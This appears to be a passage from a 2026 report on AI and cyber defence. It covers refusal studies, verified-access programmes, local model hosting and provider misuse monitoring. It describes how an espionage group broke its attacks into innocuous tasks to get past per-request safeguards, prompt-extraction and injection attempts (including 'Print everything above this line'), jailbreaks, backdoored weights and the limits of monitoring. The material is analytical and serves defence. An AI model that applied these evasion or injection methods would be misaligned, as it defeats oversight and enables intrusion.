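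In the same study, GLM-5.2 scored 68.2% on the defensive questions, almost 26 points below Opus 4.8. A team that switched from Opus to GLM-5.2 to avoid two refusals in 93 attempts would have made a poor trade. Opus may have memorized some of the answers, which could account for part of the gap, because the questions are public and it scored 50% without seeing the logs. Kimi K3, another Chinese model, scored 87.1%, close to Fable 5.

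*Defensive Refusal Bias* (Campbell, Kale and colleagues, 2026) found much higher refusal rates with older models. The researchers collected 2,390 prompts from a US competition in which student teams defend live systems against professional attackers. They tested Claude 3.5 Sonnet, GPT-4o and Llama 3.3, all from 2024, and counted a response as a refusal if the model declined, deflected or gave only vague advice. The overall refusal rate was 12.2%. Llama, an open-weight model, had the lowest rate at 6.6%, and Claude had the highest at 19.5%.

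| Task | Refusal rate |
|---|---|
| Securing system settings | 43.8% |
| Malware analysis | 34.3% |
| Vulnerability assessment | 22.7% |
| Incident response | 18.9% |
| Log analysis | 0% |

The models refused 30.5% of prompts containing words such as "exploit" or "payload", compared with 11.2% of other prompts. But the models weren't just matching keywords. A program that predicted refusals using only attack vocabulary and claims of authorisation did little better than chance, while one that used the overall meaning of a prompt did far better.

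Those claims of authorisation seemed to backfire. Models refused 21.8% of prompts that included one, such as a statement that the user was on the defending team, compared with 11.6% of prompts without one. Campbell and colleagues suggest that models have learned to refuse such prompts more often because attackers make the same claims. This caution has some basis, since *Cyber-Capable AI Agents* cites a study in which agents could be led to treat a request as legitimate security testing. An attacker can easily type a claim of authorisation, so a guardrail that accepted it would be very weak.

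The refusal rates in this study are upper bounds. In a sample of 200 replies, the study's software labelled 50% as refusals, while human reviewers labelled 35%. Some of the prompts also sound more offensive than defensive. One student wanted a program that would try default passwords on every web application on a network, and refusing that isn't obviously a mistake.

The two studies can't show whether refusals have become rarer, because they used different tasks and counted refusals differently. Neither tests current models on malware analysis, where Campbell and colleagues found one of the highest refusal rates. Measurements of models released in 2025 are harder to find. According to an early Anthropic figure relayed by Tech Jacks Solutions, Fable 5 fell back to another model in fewer than 5% of sessions on average. That average covers all users, most of whom presumably never ask about an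 exploit, so it reveals little about how often security teams encounter the fallback.

### The case for strict settings at launch

Anthropic presents the wide margin as necessary for releasing Fable 5 to the public. The underlying model is unusually good at finding and exploiting flaws, and Anthropic wanted to make its other abilities widely available without giving attackers this one. It accepted the false positives even though it expected them to frustrate users. Dianne Na Penn, a head of product at Anthropic, told Fortune (2026) at launch that some benign requests would initially be blocked and that the company was working on improvements.

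The margin also protects against jailbreaks, which are prompts that get around a model's safeguards. Many jailbreaks unlock only one narrow behaviour. If the classifier blocks a wide range of probably harmless requests, a minor jailbreak may unlock only requests in that range. Anthropic describes the Amazon researchers' bypass of Fable 5 as this kind of jailbreak.

A provider can loosen its classifiers after launch but can't take back an exploit. In August, Anthropic changed Fable 5's biology classifier to block far fewer benign requests. A month earlier, it had tightened its cybersecurity safeguards by adding the classifier that flags more harmless coding work.

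Outside researchers accept parts of this case. According to Anthropic, researchers at CAISI tested Fable 5's safeguards before and after that change and considered them extraordinarily strong, but strong safeguards can still block too many legitimate requests. Campbell and colleagues want models to refuse defenders less often while still refusing harmful requests. *A Content-Based Framework for Cybersecurity Refusal Decisions in Large Language Models* proposes weighing a request's likely harm against its value to defenders and how often legitimate users make it. Both papers appeared before Fable 5, so they support guardrails in principle rather than Fable 5's particular margin.

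David Bianco of Cisco Talos, one of the critics, agrees that guardrails make sense for ordinary business use and thinks they were a reasonable tradeoff when closed models were far ahead of open ones. Bianco argues that now that the gap has narrowed, attackers can pick a model that doesn't refuse, so refusals mainly hinder defenders.

Anthropic's own rules partly reflect this point by distinguishing flaws that only Fable 5 can find from flaws that other models can find too. Strict settings are easiest to justify for the first kind and hardest to justify for explaining a log or a malware sample, because an attacker gains little from the explanation and can get it elsewhere.

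### Anthropic's Cyber Verification Program

A verified access programme loosens the guardrails for customers whose identity and purpose the provider has checked. Anthropic's *Cyber Verification Program* describes three tiers of access, which replaced the company's single level in October 2026. The tiers cover recent Mythos, Opus and Sonnet models but not Fable.

| Tier | Permitted work | Who can apply | Approved users |
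|---|---|---|---|
| Defense Access | Incident response, malware analysis, checking vulnerabilities | Organisations and individuals | No default limit for organisations |
| Red Team Access | Authorised penetration testing, exploit development | Organisations | Up to 75 |
| Specialized Access | High-risk testing of critical systems such as power grids | Organisations | Up to 25 |

Incident response and malware analysis appear both on Fable 5's benign list and among the reasons to apply for Defense Access. An early October version of Anthropic's *Cyber Verification Program* warned that classifiers may interrupt malware analysis on the generally available models. Analysts therefore can't reliably tell from the benign list whether they need verification.

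That early version set a target of seven business days for a decision or a request for more information. By early December the target was two days for Defense Access and two weeks for Red Team Access, though heavy demand was slowing Red Team reviews. Specialized Access has no target because Anthropic reviews each applicant with the US government. Even two days is a long time during a break-in like Hugging Face's, where the agents took over several clusters within hours. A team that expects to rely on the programme therefore has to apply before an incident. After approval, its administrator usually has to assign access to the right users.

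Applicants must also secure their accounts, since a thief who stole a verified login would get the looser guardrails with it. Defense Access requires multi-factor authentication (a second proof of identity besides the password), and teams must replace their API keys at least every seven days. From 15 December 2026, it no longer allows such keys and requires phishing-resistant authentication. Red Team Access adds background checks, devices controlled by the organisation and limits on outgoing network traffic. A testing firm must also document its work, for example with a recognised accreditation. A smaller firm without one can submit evidence such as staff certifications and a redacted client report.

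Good security practice doesn't guarantee approval. Anthropic lists five factors:

- whether the organisation's work is mainly defensive
- whether Anthropic can confirm who it is
- the legal environment in which it operates, including the risk that someone could compel it to share access
- whom the work ultimately serves
- which tier it wants

Anthropic is more cautious about organisations that mainly serve military, intelligence or law-enforcement customers. A firm that investigates break-ins for the police could therefore find it harder to get approved than one that works for banks. In July Anthropic said it expected to reject some eligible applicants by mistake and that approved users might still have requests blocked.

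Approval covers only work on the organisation's own systems and independent research into flaws. A firm that serves clients needs separate approval for each service. A managed service can qualify if the firm's staff run the model and the client receives only finished work that the staff have reviewed. A defensive product can also qualify if its users can't direct the model or see its raw output. Anthropic doesn't yet accept applications for products that let customers prompt the model. Anthropic's *Bringing the cybersecurity capabilities of Claude Mythos 5 to more defenders* (2026) explains that someone with direct access can try to steer a model towards harm, while someone who receives only a patch or an alert has much less opportunity to do so.

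### OpenAI's Trusted Access for Cyber and Daybreak

OpenAI started Trusted Access for Cyber in February 2026 and now calls it Daybreak. OpenAI's *Scaling Trusted Access for Cyber with GPT‑5.5 and GPT‑5.5‑Cyber* (2026) shows how responses to the same request differ by access level. The standard GPT-5.5 refused to write an exploit for a published flaw in React, a popular web framework, and offered defensive help such as a version scanner. With Trusted Access, the same model wrote the exploit and tested it on a local server. It still refused to run the exploit against a live target, which the more permissive GPT-5.5-Cyber agreed to do.

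Daybreak has two tiers. Blue is for defensive work such as incident response and malware analysis, and Red is for advanced security testing. Only organisations can normally get Red. According to OpenAI, the effect of each tier depends on the model:

| Model | With Blue | With Red |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5, GPT-5.6 Sol, GPT-6 Sol and Luna | Fewer refusals | Fewer refusals |
| GPT-6 Astra, GPT-6.1 Sol and Terra | Standard guardrails, unless the organisation also has Red | Fewer refusals |
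| GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol | Standard guardrails | Fewer refusals |
| GPT-5.6 Cyber | No access | Fewer refusals |
| GPT-6 Cyber | No access | Fewer refusals, after separate approval |

An independent malware analyst with Blue therefore has to choose between the newest models and the more permissive ones. The setting that reduces refusals is also off by default, so an approved user who forgets to turn it on gets the standard guardrails.

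Kassianik and colleagues tested GPT-5.6 Sol before and after OpenAI granted their account the first level of verification. Its success rate on the offensive challenges rose from 9.4% to 87.2%. Its score on the defensive questions fell from 91.4% to 78.8%, for no obvious reason. The runs were on different dates and other conditions may have changed, so the comparison can't isolate the effect of verification. But the offensive result is hard to explain without a large drop in refusals.

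OpenAI lets verified users test systems they don't own if they have explicit permission. It bans them from passing Daybreak on to customers or building it into a product, and directs companies with such plans to a separate partner programme.

### Looser guardrails in return for visibility

Both providers have tied permissive access to their ability to see how customers use their models. Anthropic requires data retention by default to look for misuse, and it expects people to review what its automated systems flag. In April, OpenAI's *Trusted access for the next era of cyber defense* (2026) warned that its permissive models might come with limits on "no-visibility uses" such as zero data retention (ZDR). OpenAI reasoned that risk depends on the user and the purpose as well as the model, and that it knows less about the user and the purpose when it can't see the traffic.

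This reasoning is sound, but it creates a problem for confidential security work. The model may refuse to examine an unpublished exploit or raw evidence from a break-in for users who aren't verified, and the provider may keep a copy of what verified users submit.

Both companies have since made exceptions. Anthropic lets customers who already have a ZDR exemption for Fable or Mythos models use the verification programme with ZDR, but only for internal work. On Amazon's Bedrock, which doesn't yet support the human review that Anthropic requires, only customers with such an exemption can join the programme. OpenAI approves Daybreak and ZDR separately, so a customer needs both approvals. It allows customers to use GPT-6 Cyber with ZDR if they have set up Private Safety Processing.

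The exceptions work better for a bank investigating its own network than for a penetration-testing firm whose client forbids outside storage. With Anthropic, the firm would need Red Team Access and approval for a managed service, and the ZDR exemption for internal work would not clearly cover the client's data. OpenAI's terms appear to suit the firm better if it obtains Daybreak Red, ZDR and the client's explicit permission.

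## What it takes to run a capable model locally, and where it leaks

If a client forbids outside storage, or a team's application for verified access fails, the team needs a machine with enough memory to hold a capable model. The model's weights take up most of that memory, so their number and precision largely determine what hardware the team has to buy.

### How much memory GLM-5.2 needs

Published figures for the size of GLM-5.2 differ slightly. Z.ai's *GLM-5.2 & GLM-5.1 & GLM-5* lists 744 billion weights, while NVIDIA's model card lists 753 billion. SemiAnalysis, a research firm that covers AI hardware, reports that the released files contain 753,329,940,480.

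An extra layer accounts for the difference. GLM-5.2 has 78 main layers and one more that guesses the next few tokens, which speeds up replies. Like most of the main layers, the extra one contains 257 "experts", small networks of which the model uses only nine for any given token. Each expert consists of three grids of 6,144 by 2,048 weights, so the experts in one layer contain

257 × 3 × 6,144 × 2,048 ≈ 9.7 billion weights

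Subtracting the extra layer's parameters from 753.3 billion leaves 743.6 billion, which rounds to Z.ai's figure. The download includes that layer, so 753 billion is the better number for planning.

At 16 bits (two bytes) per weight, the files take up about 1.5 terabytes, though quantised builds need less. The set-up guide for vLLM, a widely used inference program, is *GLM-5.2* (2026), and it recommends about a fifth more GPU memory than the weights occupy.

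| Build | Weights alone | Minimum GPU memory | Hardware with enough memory |
|---|---|---|---|
| 16-bit | 1,507 GB | 1,786 GB | Two servers with eight H200 GPUs each |
| 8-bit | 753 GB | 893 GB | One server with eight H200 GPUs |
| NVIDIA's 4-bit build | 465 GB | 558 GB | Four B200 GPUs, though vLLM's example uses eight |

Storing 744 billion weights at exactly 4 bits would take only 372 GB, so NVIDIA's build is larger than its name suggests. In its number format, every 16 weights share an 8-bit scale factor, as *GLM 5.2 NVFP4*, the page for another build, explains. That raises the average to 4.5 bits. NVIDIA also compresses only the experts that the model chooses between, which hold about 725 billion weights. If the other 28.5 billion stay at 16 bits, the total is

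725 × 4.5/8 + 28.5 × 2 ≈ 465 GB

The compression seems to reduce performance only slightly. NVIDIA found that the 4-bit build scored within one point of the 8-bit build on five general tests, including science questions and tool use. None of these tests covered security work, so a team should still try both builds on an old incident.

GLM-5.2 uses only about 40 billion of its weights for each token, which makes it faster but doesn't reduce the memory it needs. All the weights have to stay in memory because the next token may need different ones. Long prompts take up more memory. The model accepts about a million tokens, enough for a very large log, but vLLM recommends eight B200 GPUs for prompts of that length.

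### Machines, money and staff

The 8-bit build fits on a single server that a company can order from a normal supplier. Dell's copy of the model card, *GLM-5.2-FP8* (2026), lists three compatible configurations, one with NVIDIA's H200 and two with AMD's GPUs.

Prices vary too much for a general figure, but invented round numbers show how the costs divide. Suppose the server costs $400,000 and lasts four years, electricity costs $15,000 a year, and the server takes up half the time of an engineer who costs $200,000 a year. The yearly cost is then

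$400,000/4 + $15,000 + $200,000/2 = $215,000

The engineer costs as much as the hardware, and half of one engineer's time can't cover nights or holidays. The team pays the same amount however little it uses the server, so each investigation costs $21,500 at ten a year and $215 at a thousand. A team that needs a large model only in emergencies would do better to rent a dedicated machine, if it can accept a cloud company holding the hardware.

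Vlcek, in *Your Security Shouldn't Depend on Someone Else's API*, argues for owning the server. Providers charge by the token, and Vlcek cites an estimate by the research firm Gartner that agents use 5 to 30 times as many tokens per task as a chatbot. Teams that pay by the token may therefore skip the least promising leads, which is where Vlcek expects serious flaws to be. On a team's own server, another token costs almost nothing until the server is full, after which the team has to queue its requests or buy a second server. The argument is strongest for alert triage, which runs all day, and weakest for incident response.

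Setting up the server also takes some expertise. An agent needs the model to call tools, but vLLM's guide recommends the latest development version instead of the stable release for combining tool calling with the extra layer's speed-up. Before an incident begins, someone has to find this out and decide whether to trust unreleased software with evidence.

Smaller models need none of this. Ibrahim, Ikram and Salama (2026), in *The Illusion of Local Privacy*, ran four of them on one workstation with 16 GB of ordinary memory and a GPU with 8 GB:

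| Model | Weights | File size at about 4 bits |
|---|---|---|
| Nemotron-3-Nano | 4 billion | 2.8 GB |
| Gemma-4-E4B | 7.5 billion | 5.3 GB |
| Qwen3.5 | 9 billion | 5.6 GB |
| Phi-4-reasoning-plus | 14 billion | 9.1 GB |

Many analysts already have a computer this powerful. The largest of the four files is about a fiftieth the size of NVIDIA's GLM-5.2 build, but it still doesn't fit entirely in the workstation's GPU memory.

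### Which security tasks need the best model

The gap between open-weight and closed models depends on the model and the task. GLM-5.2 matched a six-month-old closed model in CAISI's overall rating, but it scored far below Claude Opus 4.8 on Kassianik and colleagues' log-searching questions. Kimi K3 came much closer to Opus on those questions.

Z.ai's coding results also show GLM-5.2 further behind on some tasks than others. *GLM-5.2-FP8* reports that the model scored 81% on Terminal-Bench 2.1, a set of command-line tasks, against 85% for Opus 4.8 and 84% for GPT-5.5. On DeepSWE, a set of longer programming tasks, it scored 46%, against 58% for Opus 4.8 and 70% for GPT-5.5. Command-line work is a large part of incident response, so the Terminal-Bench result is encouraging for defenders, but neither benchmark contains security tasks.

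Open developers are also improving quickly. In August 2026 Z.ai announced GLM-5.3, which has the same base model as GLM-5.2 and differs only in its later training. SemiAnalysis lists Z.ai's own security scores for both:

| Test | What the model has to do | GLM-5.2 | GLM-5.3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| CyberGym | Find a flaw in source code and trigger it | 77.2 | 84.5 |
| ExploitBench | Produce a working exploit for a real flaw | 24.4 | 54.4 |
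| ExploitGym, 2-hour limit | Complete exploitation tasks | 29 tasks | 105 tasks |
| ExploitGym, 6-hour limit | Complete exploitation tasks | 39 tasks | 130 tasks |

In two months, the ability to find flaws rose modestly, while the number of completed exploitation tasks more than tripled. The table shows the pace of progress, but it includes no closed models and so can't show the remaining gap with them. Z.ai promised to release the weights within two weeks of the announcement. Because the base model is the same, a server bought for GLM-5.2 should be able to run GLM-5.3.

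At the other extreme, Vlcek argues that small specialist models can perform as well as frontier models on narrow security tasks. The best evidence is IBM's CyberPal 2.0, a family of models with 4 to 20 billion weights. The largest ranked first at matching vulnerabilities and bug tickets to the right type of weakness, and the smallest came second. But the closed models they beat, such as GPT-4o and o3-mini, were old by 2026.

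Vlcek also reports that a model with 4.7 billion weights, given the right supporting software, found the same well-known vulnerability as a leading closed system. Finding one known flaw is a weak test because it doesn't measure how many false alarms the model would raise in an unfamiliar codebase. Vlcek's company, AISLE, sells security software that customers can run themselves, so it benefits if buyers believe that small models are enough.

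A useful way to choose a model is to ask how easily the team would notice its mistakes. When GLM-5.2 worked out how OpenAI's agents had scrambled the data they stole from Hugging Face, the responders could check the key by trying it, since a wrong key would have produced nonsense. Explanations of scripts and timelines of events are harder to check, but an analyst can compare them with the log. A model somewhat behind the frontier is good enough for such work, and a small one may be enough for labelling bug tickets or doing an initial sort of alerts, provided people regularly check a sample.

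If a model wrongly reports that an intruder left no other backdoor, or that a codebase has no serious flaw, the team has no finding to check and may learn of the mistake only after the next break-in. The strongest model is most worth the trouble for these tasks, even if the team has to apply for verified access. A local model can still help alongside it, because different models tend to find different flaws.

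### Where a local prompt can leak

Keeping a prompt on the team's own machine keeps it from an outside provider, but other people and programs may still be able to read it. Ibrahim and colleagues put a random identifier in each test prompt, then searched for it in places where it should no longer have been. They tested llama.cpp, an inference program, and Ollama and LM Studio, two applications for running models on a personal computer. They examined four boundaries: loading the model, clearing memory, writing to disk and separating users.

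Loading was the only boundary that held. Ibrahim and colleagues fed llama.cpp damaged model files, some built by hand and others generated automatically over 24 hours. The program rejected all of them, in more than 12 million attempts, without crashing. This is reassuring but far from proof of safety, because other researchers have found ways to attack several inference programs with malicious model files.

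The leak from memory was much worse. After the model replied, 13 or 14 readable copies of each prompt remained in the server's memory. Programs make many temporary copies of a text as they process it, and normally mark the space as free without erasing it. When 12 users took turns on one server, the researchers could still recover prompts from 11 of them. A patch that erased some copies cut the recoverable text by 69%, but prompts from 11 users remained readable. Running part of the model on a GPU didn't prevent the leak, because the CPU still prepares the prompt.

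To read this leftover data, an attacker needs a program running under the same user account as the model. That is a realistic danger on an analyst's laptop, which has browser extensions and add-ons, and a smaller one on a server that runs only the model. The identifiers disappeared from the memory the researchers examined once the server program stopped, so a team can reduce the risk by restarting the program after each investigation.

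The disk results depended on the application. LM Studio wrote prompts to a plain-text log by default, and the researchers could still read them days later. An analyst who included a client's password in a prompt could leave it on the laptop after closing the conversation. Turning off one setting stopped the logging. The researchers found no prompts in Ollama's files and saw no attempt to contact the outside world in 205 sessions.

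The most serious flaw affected users who share a server. If an administrator turns on a feature that saves conversations, llama.cpp checks that a user has a valid key but not that the saved conversation belongs to that user. One user could load another's conversation in all 200 attempts. When the attacker asked the model to continue the conversation, its output revealed the other user's secret in 126 of them. A penetration-testing firm that gave each client's team a separate key would have no real separation between clients.

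Response times also leaked information about earlier prompts. The server stores its calculations for the beginnings of recent prompts so that it can reuse them. With Nemotron, the reply began after about 20 milliseconds if someone had already sent a prompt with the same beginning, and after 786 milliseconds if not. The difference remained clear over an ordinary internet connection. An attacker has to guess the text, but that may be easy if a firm starts every prompt with a standard form and the client's name.

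These tests covered small models and mainly one inference program, so the numbers may not apply to a team that runs GLM-5.2 on vLLM. But that team has no reason to assume that its server erases prompts. To find out, it would need to repeat the test with its own identifier.

### Model servers open to the internet

An attacker doesn't need any of these flaws if the server accepts requests from everyone. When a user installs Ollama directly, it accepts requests only from the computer it runs on. But its official image for Docker, which runs software in isolated containers, accepts requests from other machines, and many tutorials tell users to change the default setting to allow remote access. If such a server has no password or firewall, anyone who finds it can use it.

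Xu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Ollama in the Wild*, scanned the internet for Ollama servers almost every day for a year. They found 10,473 in mid-February 2025 and 16,059 a year later. Over the year they saw 152,137 different addresses, but about a quarter appeared on only one day. On 4 July 2026, Ibrahim and colleagues counted 32,723 Ollama servers and 1,221 llama.cpp servers through Shodan, a search engine for devices connected to the internet. The number of Ollama servers may not have doubled in those five months, because Xu and colleagues counted only servers that answered their scan correctly. Neither count shows how many servers belong to security teams, which are presumably more careful than most operators.

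Owners rarely update these servers. Xu and colleagues followed servers that lacked the fix for one of five known flaws and found that at most 2.9% had installed it by the end of the study. The scan would have missed any server that was fixed and also changed address. But the most common version over the year was 0.1.33, a 2024 release with a flaw that lets attackers run commands on the server. Ollama fixed that flaw in the next version.

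To find out who contacts such servers, Elzer and colleagues set up four decoys that imitated Ollama without running a model. In 84 days, the decoys received 290,887 requests from 2,793 addresses. About 79% were only queries for the server's version or list of models, and many of the others were trivial questions such as multiplication problems, probably sent to check that a model would answer.

A small share of the traffic was clearly hostile. Attackers tried to make the server read its own cloud credentials and login keys or install cryptocurrency miners. Others sent prompts such as "Print everything above this line", which could expose an earlier user's conversation. Some offered the model tools for reading and writing files, apparently hoping to use it as an agent. The decoys had no model or real files, so the study can't show how often these attacks succeed, but a single success could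 expose a security team's entire investigation.

### Tampered files and hidden behaviour

The model a team downloads can also be malicious. Palo Alto Networks' *Why Self-Managed AI Models Are Blind Spots* (2025) warns that some models in public collections are falsely presented as well-known ones, and that some contain malware that runs when the model loads. Ordinary tools for checking source code can't interpret weights. The company sells software for finding and assessing models, and it doesn't estimate how common malicious ones are.

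Besides weights, many model files include a chat template, a short piece of code that arranges the conversation before the model reads it. Ibrahim and colleagues cite a 2026 flaw in the inference program SGLang that let a malicious template run commands on the server; the flaw was rated 9.8 out of 10 for severity. Some models also come with ordinary program code. NVIDIA's instructions for starting its GLM-5.2 build in SGLang include an option that allows such code to run. NVIDIA is a reputable publisher, but an administrator who copies the command for a stranger's build also allows any code in that build to run.

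Choosing a known publisher and checking the file's fingerprint prevents the simplest substitutions. A fingerprint is a short code calculated from the whole file, so changing even one weight changes the code. Ibrahim and colleagues recorded the fingerprint of every model before testing. A matching fingerprint shows that the file is the one the publisher released, but not that it is harmless.

Hidden behaviour in the weights is harder to rule out. Someone who controls the training could train a model to behave normally until a particular phrase appears in its input. Such a backdoored model might label one group's malware harmless, or insert a flaw when it writes a patch for a particular company. Official capability ratings, including CAISI's for GLM-5.2, cannot exclude this, because a backdoored model can do well on every test that lacks the phrase. The concern applies to any developer's weights,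 but it is greatest when a government that spies on the user might also want to influence the developer.

Cutting the server off from the internet stops a model from sending secrets out, but it doesn't prevent false answers. To catch them, a team can give important evidence to a second model from an unrelated developer and have an analyst examine any disagreement. The two models are unlikely to share a backdoor, though they may still make the same mistake.

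### What the operator has to do

The provider of a hosted model handles much of its security. A team that hosts its own model does this work itself, starting with a list of the models it runs. Palo Alto Networks points out that any developer can install a model on a virtual machine without telling the security staff, who then can't protect it.

The default access controls are too weak for sensitive work. The Docker command that vLLM's guide recommends for GLM-5.2 sets no password, accepts requests from other machines and gives the container almost complete control over the host computer. This is convenient for testing, but a server that holds evidence should accept requests only from named users over a closed network, and its container should have as few rights as possible. Because a valid key may not separate users, a firm with several clients should run a separate copy of the server for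 each one, or at least restart the server and delete saved conversations before switching clients.

Patching covers the model, the inference program, the drivers and the applications around them. The update system can itself be vulnerable. Ibrahim and colleagues cite a flaw in Ollama's automatic updater for Windows that reportedly remained unfixed after the usual 90 days' notice. One of the attackers that Elzer and colleagues recorded labelled a request with the flaw's number. On an isolated network, staff can check each update before they carry it in, but the server may run old software for months.

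A full audit log contains the same secrets as the prompts, so it should go into the same protected storage as the evidence, with the same deletion date, and not into a text file on an analyst's laptop. A separate log with only names, times and tool calls is enough for daily checks and does little harm if it leaks.

Agents need the closest monitoring because no provider will notice if a local one misbehaves. Evidence can mislead an agent, since a malicious program or stolen e-mail may contain instructions for any AI that reads it to ignore a file or run a command. An agent that investigates a break-in should therefore work on copies of the evidence, with no internet access and no credentials for live systems. If it recommends revoking a key or shutting down a server, a person should check the evidence before making the change.

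## What providers' monitoring sees and what it loses

Providers of hosted models search their customers' traffic for misuse and have found break-ins in progress this way. This API-based safety monitoring covers only traffic that reaches the provider, so providers cannot see how an attacker or a hospital uses a model running on a private server.

### From a single request to a ban

Monitoring starts with the safety classifier, which needs no stored data, so it also works for customers with zero data retention (ZDR). But OpenAI says it currently checks each of these customers' interactions separately, while some serious risks show up only across several.

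Cross-request detection analyses many requests, sessions or accounts together, so the provider has to store the traffic for a while. Anthropic gave this as the reason for its 30-day storage rule of June 2026. In Anthropic's simplest example, an attacker sends hundreds of slight variations of one prompt, hoping one will work. A single variation may look like an ordinary question unless the provider sees it alongside the others. Espionage and extortion campaigns are harder to recognise because the operators spread the work over many tasks, sometimes from several accounts. Anthropic also mentions stolen customer credentials. A thief with a valid key looks like the customer until someone compares the new traffic with the customer's usual traffic.

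Some invented numbers show why weak evidence adds up. Suppose 1 customer in 1,000 is an attacker, and attackers are twice as likely as other customers to send a certain kind of request, such as one to scan a network. One such request raises the chance that the sender is an attacker from 0.1% to only 0.2%. If the same customer sends ten different requests of this kind, and each is independent evidence, the odds become

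1/999 × 2^10 ≈ 1.03

or about even. In practice the requests aren't independent, and a penetration tester might send all ten in an afternoon. The provider therefore needs something in the history that a tester's work would lack, such as thirty unrelated targets in several countries.

A human reviewer can then confirm the misuse or dismiss the false alarm. If the misuse is real, the provider bans the accounts and may warn the victims and the authorities. The warnings matter because the victims may not be the provider's customers and may have no other way to learn about the attack early.

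### The espionage campaign of September 2025

Anthropic's *Disrupting the first reported AI-orchestrated cyber espionage campaign* (2025) describes the best-documented case. In mid-September 2025, Anthropic detected a group using Claude Code to break into organisations' networks. It attributes the campaign to a Chinese state-sponsored group. The group targeted roughly 30 organisations, including technology companies, financial institutions, chemical manufacturers and government agencies. Anthropic confirmed a handful of successful break-ins.

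The group's software divided each attack into small technical tasks, such as scanning for flaws or testing a credential. Each task looked legitimate in isolation, so checks on single requests did not stop the campaign. Claude did 80 to 90% of the hands-on work. In one example, it spent one to four hours finding and exploiting a flaw, and a human operator spent two to ten minutes reviewing the findings and approving the attack. At its peak, the group sent thousands of requests, at a rate of several operations per second. No human team could match that rate, and the sustained activity eventually triggered detection.

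Anthropic then investigated for ten days. It banned accounts as it identified them, notified affected organisations and worked with the authorities. Afterwards it improved its cyber classifiers and began developing earlier warning systems. It reports when it detected the campaign but not when the campaign began, so outsiders can't work out how long detection took, though it clearly took long enough for some of the break-ins to succeed.

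Anthropic's records contained evidence that no single victim had. They covered several targets and showed where humans had stepped in. They also showed far more data going into Claude than text coming out, a sign that the group was using it to sort through stolen files.

But Anthropic could see only what the group did with Claude. It found signs that the group had handed its access to other teams for longer operations, which Anthropic could not see unless those teams also used Claude. The transcripts were also unreliable. Claude often exaggerated its results and sometimes claimed to have obtained credentials that didn't work, so investigators could not treat its account of a break-in as proof that one had happened.

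### What later reports add

Anthropic's *Detecting and countering misuse of AI* (2026) describes operations that the company disrupted between December 2025 and August 2026. Five of them involved break-ins:

| Operators | Reach | Some of what they took |
|---|---|---|
| Russian espionage group | More than 20 organisations targeted, mostly in Ukraine and elsewhere in Europe | Mail records from at least eight organisations |
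| Chinese-speaking group | About 50 organisations targeted | Citizens' records from a Southeast Asian government agency |
| French-speaking hacktivist | 42 targets, with internal access to at least 14 | About 140,000 records, including people's political opinions |
| Suspected affiliates of ShinyHunters, an extortion group | About 200 organisations through one software supplier | More than a terabyte from a technology provider |
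| Russian-speaking criminal | About 30 AI companies attacked in four days | An AI vendor's keys for several providers' models |

The hacktivist worked for a month entirely on API keys stolen from Anthropic's customers, and one ShinyHunters affiliate used a single stolen key for about three weeks. Some break-ins in these cases took only two or three hours. Monitoring that takes weeks to stop an attacker can end a campaign, but it comes too late to protect the early victims.

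Anthropic found no malicious cyber activity on its Fable or Mythos models and says their safeguards greatly reduce what an attacker can do with these models. This is weak evidence that the storage rule works, because Fable 5 was on public sale for only about two of the nine months and attackers could still use the older models.

Anthropic first learned of a Russian influence operation in the Central African Republic from All Eyes on Wagner, an investigative project, rather than from its own monitoring. Anthropic may see an influence operation while the people running it are still writing the material, but it has to rely on public sources and other platforms to learn what happens after publication.

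OpenAI describes the same limit. *Disrupting malicious uses of AI* (2026) explains that attackers seldom keep to one platform and may use different models at different points in their work. The cases OpenAI published in February 2026, in *Disrupting malicious uses of our models* (2026), are mostly scams and influence operations. A few months earlier, *Disrupting malicious uses of AI* (2025) described a probably Russian influence operation that used ChatGPT to write prompts apparently meant for other companies' video models. OpenAI had disrupted the same operation before, so a ban had not ended it.

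Google has the advantage of running both a model, Gemini, and a large incident-response business, Mandiant. The May 2026 edition of Google Threat Intelligence Group's *GTIG AI Threat Tracker* reports that APT45, a North Korean group, sent Gemini thousands of repetitive prompts to analyse known flaws and test exploits for them. It also describes criminals who planned to use a previously unknown flaw to bypass two-factor authentication in a popular administration tool. Gemini's traffic probably could not have revealed this plan, since Google doesn't believe the criminals used Gemini. But Google is highly confident that they used some AI model, because their script was full of textbook-style explanations and included an invented severity score. Google worked with the tool's maker to disclose the flaw and may have stopped the attack before it began.

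These reports cover only attackers who were caught, and Anthropic says it selected its most notable and novel cases. None of them shows what fraction of misuse the providers detect.

### What the provider loses depends on who leaves

When defenders run models on their own machines, the provider loses examples of harmless work that looks like an attack. A reviewer who clears a penetration tester's flagged prompt has found a case where the classifier is too strict. With fewer such cases and fewer customers complaining about refusals, the provider has fewer examples to correct its classifiers with and less reason to correct them. The loss may be modest, because many of the most secretive teams would otherwise have insisted on ZDR or avoided hosted models.

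When customers host a model themselves, its developer also can't see accidents involving their agents. OpenAI gives the example of an agent that carries on after its user has told it to stop. If this happened to ten customers of a hosted model, the provider could notice the pattern and fix the model for everyone. If it happened to ten hospitals running GLM-5.2 locally, each could investigate its own accident, but Z.ai can't automatically collect cases from servers it doesn't run, so it would learn of the problem only if a hospital reported it.

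When attackers move to self-hosted models, the provider can no longer recognise their campaigns, ban them or warn their next victims. A ban may push an attacker to make that move, so a provider that gets better at catching attackers could end up seeing fewer of them.

By contrast, providers can still see what attackers do with stolen accounts. The hacktivist's month on stolen keys shows that detection can be slow, but the provider could see the traffic, and it can cancel a stolen key as soon as it recognises one. The rightful owner has a reason to help because they are paying the bill.

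When attackers hijack a self-hosted model, no AI provider is monitoring it, so only the server's owner or whoever supplies its network connection is in a position to notice. *Hackers hijack exposed AI models to launch cyberattacks at victims' expense* (Markovic, 2026) describes attackers who built an AI agent that takes over exposed models and uses them to steal credentials and mine cryptocurrency. A security team that leaves its own model server open could therefore end up supplying attackers with computing power.

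### How many attackers run their own models

Cisco Talos claims that state-sponsored attackers "simply moved their research to self-hosted, unconstrained models" after providers banned them. It gives no figures or named cases. The claim is plausible, but the public evidence mostly shows attackers using both local and hosted models.

*Google finds AI agent writing and launching exploits* (Markovic, 2026) describes a system called exploit_agent, which Google found on a server that an attacker had left exposed. The system was connected to several leading models and several local ones. It compared popular web applications before and after a security fix, looked for the flaw, wrote an exploit and ran it without human involvement. The server also held data stolen from victims. The operator kept API keys for hosted models even though local ones were available.

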